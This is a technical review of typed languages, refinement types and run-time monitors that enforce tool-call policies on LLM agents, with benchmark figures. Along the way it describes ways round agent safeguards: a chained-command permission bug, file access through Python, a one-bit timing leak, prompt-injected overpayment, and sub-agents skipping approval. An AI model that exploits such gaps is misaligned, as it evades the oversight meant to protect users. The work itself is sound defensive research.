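Odersky and colleagues tested how well models can write Scala with capture checking, which is rare in the text that models learn from. On the airline and retail tasks of τ²-bench, all three models tested scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls. The researchers think the typed results and the compiler's error messages helped. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues from GitHub, MiniMax solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it, a difference of five issues.

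On τ²-bench, between 0.32% and 7.93% of the programs needed a retry, depending on the model and the domain. Those programs averaged 1.06 to 1.39 retries. The common mistakes had little to do with capabilities. For instance, models forgot that a value might be missing, or wrote `$50` inside a string where Scala requires `$$50`.

With DeepSeek V4 Flash, LACUNA solved 76.0% of 392 τ²-bench tasks, compared with 90.0% for ordinary tool calls. The difference is about 55 tasks, though Zhao and colleagues describe the results as on par. The compiler rejected 22.4% of the model's programs in the retail domain, where tasks averaged 7.1 retries. It rejected 89% of the programs that the smaller Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite wrote in the telecom domain, but that model also did badly there with ordinary tool calls, so typed code was not its main problem.

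The two studies used different models and settings. LACUNA turns every customer message into a new hole, and its models ran with reasoning switched off, so it isn't clear how much of the gap comes from type checking. On BrowseComp-Plus, a set of difficult research questions, DeepSeek V4 Flash answered 27.1% correctly and the compiler rejected 8.6% of its programs. Zhao and colleagues conclude that type checking doesn't reduce accuracy, but they didn't compare these results with runs without it.

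Stronger models seem to write valid programs with few retries. In the ELBA experiments, runs needed 0.13 retries on average, and only 7 of 2,688 used up their retries without producing a valid program. Weaker models remain safe but may achieve little, because a rejected program never runs.

Someone also has to write the typed library. TACIT's reusable part is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and each τ²-bench domain needed a few hundred more to describe its tools. Odersky and colleagues say this is similar in length to the JSON schemas it replaces.

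### External commands and timing

Once a program starts another process, the type system can't control what that process does. TACIT can restrict the code to a list of allowed commands, and Odersky and colleagues recommend keeping the list short and adding a sandbox. Their examples of safe commands are `git diff` and `sbt`, Scala's build tool. But `sbt` is a poor choice for an agent that can edit the project, because it runs the project's build file, which can contain any Scala code.

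A typed language does reduce the need for such commands. Coding agents usually work through a shell, where a permission system has to evaluate each command by its text. Zhou and colleagues cite a March 2026 bug in Claude Code where the permission check covered only the first of several commands joined with `&&`. They also note that a rule against reading a file fails if the agent can start Python and read it from there. In ELBA, the model can do its calculations and file operations in Haskell, so the developer can leave out the shell.

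Timing leaks are harder to prevent. A pure function can't send a secret, but it can run for a long time if the secret's first bit is 1 and finish immediately if it is 0. The delay before the model's next step then reveals the bit. Odersky and colleagues place this kind of leak outside TACIT's scope and give a one-bit leak as their example. An attacker could repeat the process to learn more bits. Limiting the number of programs that touch a wrapped value would help, as would making every such program take the same time, but neither is part of TACIT.

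### Where a refinement would help

Both Zhou and colleagues and Zhao and colleagues name refinement types as a possible extension. The list of hosts in TACIT is an obvious place to start. The type of the request could require every host to be on the manifest:

```
requestNetwork : {hosts : Set Host | hosts ⊆ allowed(D)} → ...
```

If the model's program contains the text `attacker.test`, the checker can reject the program before it runs. In the refined dispatcher, the host arrives as data, so only a run-time test can catch it.

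Other values are still unknown when the compiler reads the program. Suppose `pay` requires an amount from 1 to 50, and the model writes this:

```scala
val total = parseAmount(invoice)
pay("USDC", total)
```

Nothing in the program limits `total`, so the solver can return a counterexample such as 51 and the checker rejects the program. The error goes back to the model, which can add a test:

```scala
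val total = parseAmount(invoice)
if 0 < total && total <= 50 then pay("USDC", total)
else askUser(total)
```

The proof has the same form as the one for `handle`, but here the model writes the test, and the checker has to verify a new program every time. A test inside `pay` would also stop an excessive payment, but the program might then stop halfway, after it has marked the invoice as paid. With the refinement, the model has to decide in advance what happens if the amount is too high. None of the three systems has been tested with refinements, so nobody knows how often models would write code that a solver accepts.

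A refinement can also apply to the whole program. AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026), an article based on a talk by the programming-language designer Erik Meijer, describes his proposal to apply proof-carrying code to agents. The model returns a plan as data with a proof that the plan is safe, and a separate program carries out the plan only if the proof is valid. While Meijer was preparing the talk, Claude Code ran a Perl command that erased the contents of one of his source files.

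The article includes a small example in Lean. A plan can read a file, remove a file or finish with an answer. `NoDeletion` is a condition that holds only for plans without a removal, and the program that carries out plans can accept only this type:

```lean
def CheckedPlan := { plan : FilePlan // NoDeletion plan }
```

This is Lean's notation for the refinement type of plans that satisfy `NoDeletion`. A plan can depend on what a file contains, because each reading step is followed by a function that takes the contents and returns the rest of the plan. The proof must therefore show that the rest of the plan deletes nothing, whatever the file contains.

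The condition covers only what its author thought to forbid. The command that damaged Meijer's file emptied it rather than deleting it. A plan in the example can't do this because there is no operation for writing to a file. If a developer added one and allowed it in `NoDeletion`, a plan that emptied the file would pass. AI Engineer also notes that the proof covers only the plan, so it wouldn't help if the program that carries out the plan secretly deleted files while reading them.

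## Rules about order, totals and data flow

`NoDeletion` is a condition on a whole plan. The refined dispatcher tests each tool call separately, so it gives the same answer to the same call whatever happened earlier in the session. Some common rules depend on the earlier calls:

- Authenticate the customer before issuing a refund.
- Spend at most 100 in total.
- Never send out text that came from a private file.

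A condition on the call alone cannot enforce rules about order, totals or data flow, so the condition needs a second input that records the session so far. A refund call looks the same whether or not the customer has logged in. A payment of 40 may be allowed as the first of the session but exceed the session's spending limit as the third. A message may be harmless or a leak, depending on where the model found the text.

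### A running total in the type

Suppose a billing skill may pay up to 50 per call, and a false email gets the model to pay three invoices of 40:

| Payment | Within the limit of 50? | Total afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| 40 | yes | 40 |
| 40 | yes | 80 |
| 40 | yes | 120 |

To stop the third payment, the runtime has to keep a state s that includes the amount spent so far. The payment function takes the current state and returns a new one:

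```
pay : s:State
    → {a : Int | 0 < a ∧ a ≤ 50 ∧ spent(s) + a ≤ 100}
    → {s' : State | spent(s') = spent(s) + a}
```

The last line updates the state. If `pay` returned the old state unchanged, it would not type-check, because `a` is positive and the total has to grow by `a`.

The code that handles the model's call tests the amount against the current total before it calls `pay`. If b is the result of that test, the verification condition is:

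```
for every state s, integer a and Boolean b:
  ((b ⇔ 0 < a ∧ a ≤ 50 ∧ spent(s) + a ≤ 100) ∧ b)
    ⇒  0 < a ∧ a ≤ 50 ∧ spent(s) + a ≤ 100
```

This has the same form as the condition for `handle`. A second condition shows that the total stays within the limit after the update:

```
(spent(s) + a ≤ 100  ∧  spent(s') = spent(s) + a)  ⇒  spent(s') ≤ 100
```

Both use only linear arithmetic. If the session starts with a total of 0, then by induction no later total exceeds 100. When the third payment arrives, the test fails because 80 + 40 is more than 100, and the runtime refuses the call.

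There is still a hole. Nothing in the type of `pay` requires the caller to use the latest state:

```
s1 = pay(s0, 40)
s2 = pay(s0, 40)
s3 = pay(s0, 40)
```

Each line passes the original state s0, in which the total is 0, so the checker accepts all three and the program spends 120. A retry queue that stored an old copy of the state could cause the same error.

### Evidence that can be used only once

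Swamy, Chen and Chugh (2010), in *Enforcing Stateful Authorization and Information Flow Policies in FINE*, close this hole by adding affine types to refinement types. A program may use a variable with an affine type at most once. FINE, their programming language, splits the state into two parts. The facts themselves are an ordinary value s, which the program can read as often as it likes. Separately, an affine token of type `StateIs s` is the evidence that s is the current state. With such a token, the payment function becomes:

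```
pay : s:State
    → {a : Int | 0 < a ∧ a ≤ 50 ∧ spent(s) + a ≤ 100}
    → StateIs s
    → (s' : {s' : State | spent(s') = spent(s) + a},  StateIs s')
```

The first payment uses up the token for s0 and returns a token for s1. The second line of the faulty program requires a token for s0, which is no longer available, so the checker rejects the program. The constructor of `StateIs` is private to its module, as `Ok` is in the `Gate` module, so other code can't forge a token.

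FINE's main example models CONTINUE, a web application for managing academic conferences. Authors may submit papers only until the chair closes submissions. Closing submissions uses up the token for the old state, so no code can present that state afterwards as evidence that a submission is allowed. CONTINUE's developers had reported that almost all the interesting bugs they encountered concerned authorization. The model covers 9 phases of a conference and 12 kinds of action.

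The split also makes the proofs easier. Conditions in FINE mention only ordinary values, so the standard solver Z3 can prove them. Conditions on affine values would have needed a prover for linear logic, in which using an assumption consumes it. Such provers were still experimental. The checker had to prove 195 conditions for eight example programs totaling 2,222 lines. Parsing and checking took under 18 seconds on a desktop computer of the time. A soundness theorem guarantees that a well-typed program uses each affine value at most once.

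The guarantee covers the program's record of what it has spent, but things outside the type can make that record wrong. Two processes that each start with a token for a total of 0 can spend 100 each. Sub-agents have the same problem unless they share one total. *APPA* (2026) describes a policy system for agents that keeps a single event log for a whole tree of agent runs, and a spending limit needs such a log. A payment may also time out, so that the runtime can't determine whether the money moved. The cautious choice is to count the amount as spent until the payment service confirms that it wasn't.

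JavaScript and Python have no affine types, so a developer can keep the total in one private variable and let a single function check and update it. The function must reserve the amount before it waits for the payment service. Otherwise, two calls for 20 can both read a total of 80, and both will pass.

### Which call comes first

An order rule sometimes needs no state at all. In FINE, `login` checks a password and returns a credential whose type contains the user's name. A refund function can require that credential:

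```
refund : u:User → cred u → {o : Order | owner(o) = u} → Result
```

`refund` requires a credential that only a successful `login` for the same user produces, so the login must have come first. The model never handles the credential, because it emits JSON and the runtime keeps the credential and supplies it to the call. This method doesn't cover expiry, since a credential from before a logout still has the right type. To cover expiry, the login must be a fact in the current state, with a token as evidence.

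Order rules are harder to check when the two calls are in different functions or different agents. In one bug report about the coding agent Goose, a parent session required approval for sensitive tools, but a sub-agent started in automatic mode and ran them without asking the parent's user. Tan, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *ETAS*, cite this report as a reason to check order across a whole agent program. In ETAS, their programming language for agents, a developer can write:

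```
spec ApprovedApply = Approval.request >> Repo.apply;
```

Under this rule, a program may request a change to the repository only after it has requested approval. The compiler summarises the requests that each function can make, in order, including those of the functions it calls. It turns the rule into a finite automaton, a machine with a fixed number of states that reads one request at a time, and runs the summary through it:

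| Requests in the summary | What the compiler does |
|---|---|
| approval, then possibly a change | accepts the program, with a proof that the rule holds |
| change, then approval | rejects the program |
| either order, depending on a branch | accepts the program and keeps a monitor |

The monitor in the last row is the same automaton, running alongside the program and refusing any request that would break the rule. Tan and colleagues call it a residual monitor. Flanagan's hybrid checker also leaves undecided cases to run time, but the test it inserts examines a single value rather than a sequence of requests.

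The summary also includes requests that never reach the outside world. A developer testing an agent can install a handler that intercepts and discards every write. In most languages with effect types, an intercepted write disappears from the function's type, so a write without approval would go unnoticed during the test and take effect in production. ETAS keeps intercepted writes in the summary and applies the same rules to them.

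Tan and colleagues prove seven numbered results about a core version of the language. The main ones are:

- A well-typed program finishes with a value of the right type, keeps running, or stops with an error such as a refusal.
- The requests in any run fit the summary, and the operations that the host carries out stay within the declared set.
- Every run obeys its order rules under the monitor. If the compiler has proved a rule, removing that rule's monitor changes no successful run and lets no violation through.
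- A handler can't remove a request from the record or bypass the other checks.

The third result is a sound form of Metere's erasure-stable rule. A compiler may drop a run-time check once it has proved that the check can't fail, but ETAS keeps the host's separate permission check. All of this assumes that every external operation goes through the runtime.

The rules mention only the names of operations. `ApprovedApply` is satisfied as soon as the program has requested approval, even if the human says no, and one request covers every later change. The program has to test the answer with an ordinary `if`, and the host has to decide whether the approval covers this change. The host, which has access to arguments and history, would also have to enforce the spending limit, because an automaton that reads only operation names can count payments but can't add up their amounts.

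The safety tests are small. Tan and colleagues ran the file-reading part of a coding agent through ten scenarios with scripted model replies. Four finished normally and six stopped at the expected point. In separate tests of the compiler, it accepted two valid programs and rejected four faulty ones. There was no attacker and no competing system, and the tests don't measure the effect of the rules on task success. (A question-answering agent that repeatedly revised its own ETAS code improved from 69.9% to 78.9%, but the comparison was with its own first version.)

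### Making the model try another call

ETAS requires developers to write the agent in a new language. Agent-C, which Kamath, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents*, describe, works with ordinary tool calls and has no refinement types. One of its rules for a shop's customer-service agent amounts to this:

```
read_order(o)  requires an earlier call  u = find_user(email)
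               with  u ≠ not_found  and  owner(o) = u
```

Before the agent reads an order, it must have looked up the user, the lookup must have succeeded, and that user must own the order. Checking ownership requires a query to the shop's database, so a rule can depend on facts that never appeared in the conversation. A similar rule allows a refund only to the original payment method or a gift card. Without it, Claude Sonnet 4.5 tried to refund a credit-card purchase to a PayPal account because the user insisted, although the system prompt forbade such refunds.

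When the model proposes a call, Agent-C appends it to the record of the session, translates the record and the rules into a formula, and has an SMT solver check whether they are consistent. If they are not, the model has to generate something else. With an open-weight model, Agent-C can discard the offending part of the output and resume from there. Commercial providers don't expose the probabilities this requires, so for GPT-5 and Claude, Agent-C requests a whole new call. After a limited number of failed attempts, it records an error that the model can read on its next turn.

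Kamath and colleagues tested Agent-C on the retail and airline tasks of τ-bench, the predecessor of τ²-bench. The baseline here is the same model without a guardrail:

| Model | Conformance, baseline | Conformance, Agent-C | Task success, baseline | Task success, Agent-C |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 83.7% | 100% | 66.1% | 70.6% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 77.4% | 100% | 71.8% | 75.2% |

A monitor that refuses every call that breaks the rules should produce 100% conformance, so those figures mainly show that the implementation works. Task success is more interesting, but it counts only tasks completed without breaking the policy, so some of the gain may come from tasks that the baseline also completed, but with a violation. The open-weight model Qwen3-32B improved more. Its success rate on the retail tasks was 25.5% without a guardrail, 37.4% with AgentSpec, an earlier rule-based monitor,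 and 53.3% with Agent-C. DynaGuard, which uses a second language model as the judge, reduced the rate to 9.6%.

### Checking a plan before the first call

Blocking calls can leave an agent with no way to finish. The clearest example in *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, a survey by Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026), is a τ-bench study in which a guardrail blocked 94% of unsafe actions. In most settings, the agents still completed fewer than 5% of tasks both safely and correctly, and they kept finding other unsafe routes. Dantas and colleagues warn that this finding rests on a single study.

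*SOTERIA* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026) has the model write a plan before it calls any tools. The plan is a graph in which each step can call a tool, and conditions on the results determine the next step. The verification language Dafny checks that every call meets the tool's precondition, that the plan can't get stuck, and that every path obeys the policy. For example, a model might plan to cancel a flight reservation by looking it up, checking that the customer booked within the last 24 hours, and cancelling it. If the policy also requires a check that no flight in the reservation has already departed, the verifier rejects the plan before any tool runs and reports the problem to the model.

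The model can still depart from its plan, so a monitor checks every actual call against the same rules. If the monitor blocks a call, the model can look for another way to proceed among the plan's remaining steps.

He and colleagues used 207 tasks from three benchmarks: 50 airline and 114 retail tasks from τ²-bench, and 43 from Toolathlon, which has longer tasks with files and documents. The baselines were a plain agent and three guardrail systems. This table gives the share of tasks completed without a violation, for the best baseline and then for Soteria:

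| Model | Airline | Retail | Toolathlon |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4-mini | 50.0% → 60.0% | 20.2% → 35.1% | 2.3% → 11.6% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 36.0% → 62.0% | 38.6% → 45.6% | 2.3% → 16.3% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 30.0% → 70.0% | 31.6% → 56.1% | 4.7% → 9.3% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 56.0% → 88.0% | 46.5% → 90.4% | 11.6% → 18.6% |

Soteria had no violations in any of these tests. That count uses revised rules, because the people who wrote the rules corrected some and added missing ones while auditing the results. On Toolathlon, the plain Opus agent completed 30.2% of tasks, including those with violations, and Soteria completed 18.6%. The monitor therefore seems to have prevented some completions there, although more tasks were completed without violations.

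Verifying the plan helped less than adding the monitor. On the airline tasks, GPT-5.4-mini with an unverified plan and no monitor succeeded 44% of the time, with 13 violations. Verifying the plan raised this to 46% with 10 violations, and reusable sub-plans raised it to 50% with 12. Adding the monitor raised success to 60% and eliminated violations. For Gemini, verification alone didn't change the success rate. An operator who can adopt only one of the two should probably start with the monitor.

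Soteria raised Opus's cost per airline task from $0.32 to $0.80 because it makes a new plan each time the customer replies. Toolathlon tasks need only one plan, and Soteria cut the cost per task from $0.97 to $0.43.

### Where private text may go

FINE can also track data by attaching the name of its source file to the type of a string. Suppose Alice and an administrator can read both `a.txt` and `ab.txt`, but Bob can read only `ab.txt`. A program that joins the text of the two files may write the result to `a.txt`, but writing it to `ab.txt` is a type error because Bob could then read text from `a.txt`. In general, data may flow from one file to another only if everyone who can read the second can also read the first. FINE relies on the developer to state this rule correctly and would accept it written backwards.

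Labels of this kind follow a string through ordinary code, but they can't follow it through a language model. The model combines everything in its input, and nothing in its output records which words came from where. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) lists the choice of which parts of a model's context to label separately as an unsolved difficulty. The safe approach is to give the whole context one label. In *APPA*, a label pairs a set of permitted readers with a trust level, and combining two labels keeps only the readers they share and the lower trust level:

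```
private notes     readers {Alice, Bob}    trust high
web page          readers everyone        trust low
model's context   readers {Alice, Bob}    trust low
```

*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) describes a policy that allows a call to send data out only if every recipient may read it. With this label, the runtime would refuse an email to Carol even if it said only "Thanks". The same paper warns that a context's label can quickly become too restrictive. TACIT's `Classified` values avoid this by keeping private text out of the model's context, as long as the model doesn't need to read it.

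Somebody has to supply the labels for tools on remote servers. In *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents*, Doshi, Hong and colleagues (2026) propose requiring every Model Context Protocol tool to have labels for what it can do, whether its data is confidential, and whether its output is trustworthy. In their example, a user adds a medical appointment that clashes with a work meeting. The agent moves the meeting and mentions the treatment in its email to colleagues, so private information leaks without an attacker. With labels, the runtime could block data marked private from flowing to a tool marked `external_write`, and ask the user when a label is "unsure".

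A capability label would also give the dispatcher some of the information it needs for `cap`, although the operator has to trust the server that supplies the label. There is little evidence for the proposal so far. Doshi and colleagues modelled it in Alloy, a tool that searches every sequence of steps up to a fixed length. The search found leaks only when the policies were absent, and with the policies in place the agent could still reschedule an event and notify people safely. They did not run an agent on a benchmark, so there is no baseline or figure for task success.

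### What a monitor can and cannot enforce

Fred Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) studied monitors that observe a program as it runs and stop it before it breaks a rule. Such monitors can enforce only safety properties, which are rules where every violation happens at a definite moment and can't be repaired later. The first two rules are safety properties. Logging in after the refund doesn't undo the violation, and neither does spending less after the total has passed 100. To enforce these rules, the monitor needs an accurate record of the session and the power to refuse the next call.

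A monitor can't enforce a rule that something must eventually happen. Doshi and colleagues' calendar agent has to email every attendee after it changes an event. A monitor could refuse all other calls until the emails have gone out, but if the model simply stops, the emails are never sent. Agent-C accepts rules such as "after opening a file, close it", but if the model tries to end the session with the file still open, Agent-C can only end it with an error. Soteria goes a little further by checking that every successful path through the plan contains the required follow-up, but the model still has to carry it out. Where the follow-up is predictable, the runtime can do it itself, for example by sending a standard notification.

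The third rule fails for a different reason. Whether a message reveals a private file depends on what the agent would have sent if the file had been different. Suppose two agents each read notes about a possible merger and then send one word to an outsider. The first always sends "yes", while the second sends "yes" if the notes confirm the merger and "no" otherwise. If the notes confirm the merger, both agents make the same calls, but only the second leaks information. A monitor that receives only the calls can't block the second agent without also blocking the first.

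Monitors therefore enforce a stricter rule, such as no outside messages after the agent has read a private file. That rule is a safety property, and it stops both agents. This strictness is probably part of why ELBA completed fewer Slack tasks with its policies on. A refusal can also leak information if the program reaches the forbidden call only when the notes confirm the merger. For this reason, FINE, unlike Flanagan's system, doesn't automatically insert run-time checks when a proof fails.

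If both agents were programs in FINE, the checker could tell them apart, because the first agent's message doesn't use the notes. But when a model emits one call at a time, there is no source code to check for whether a message uses the notes.
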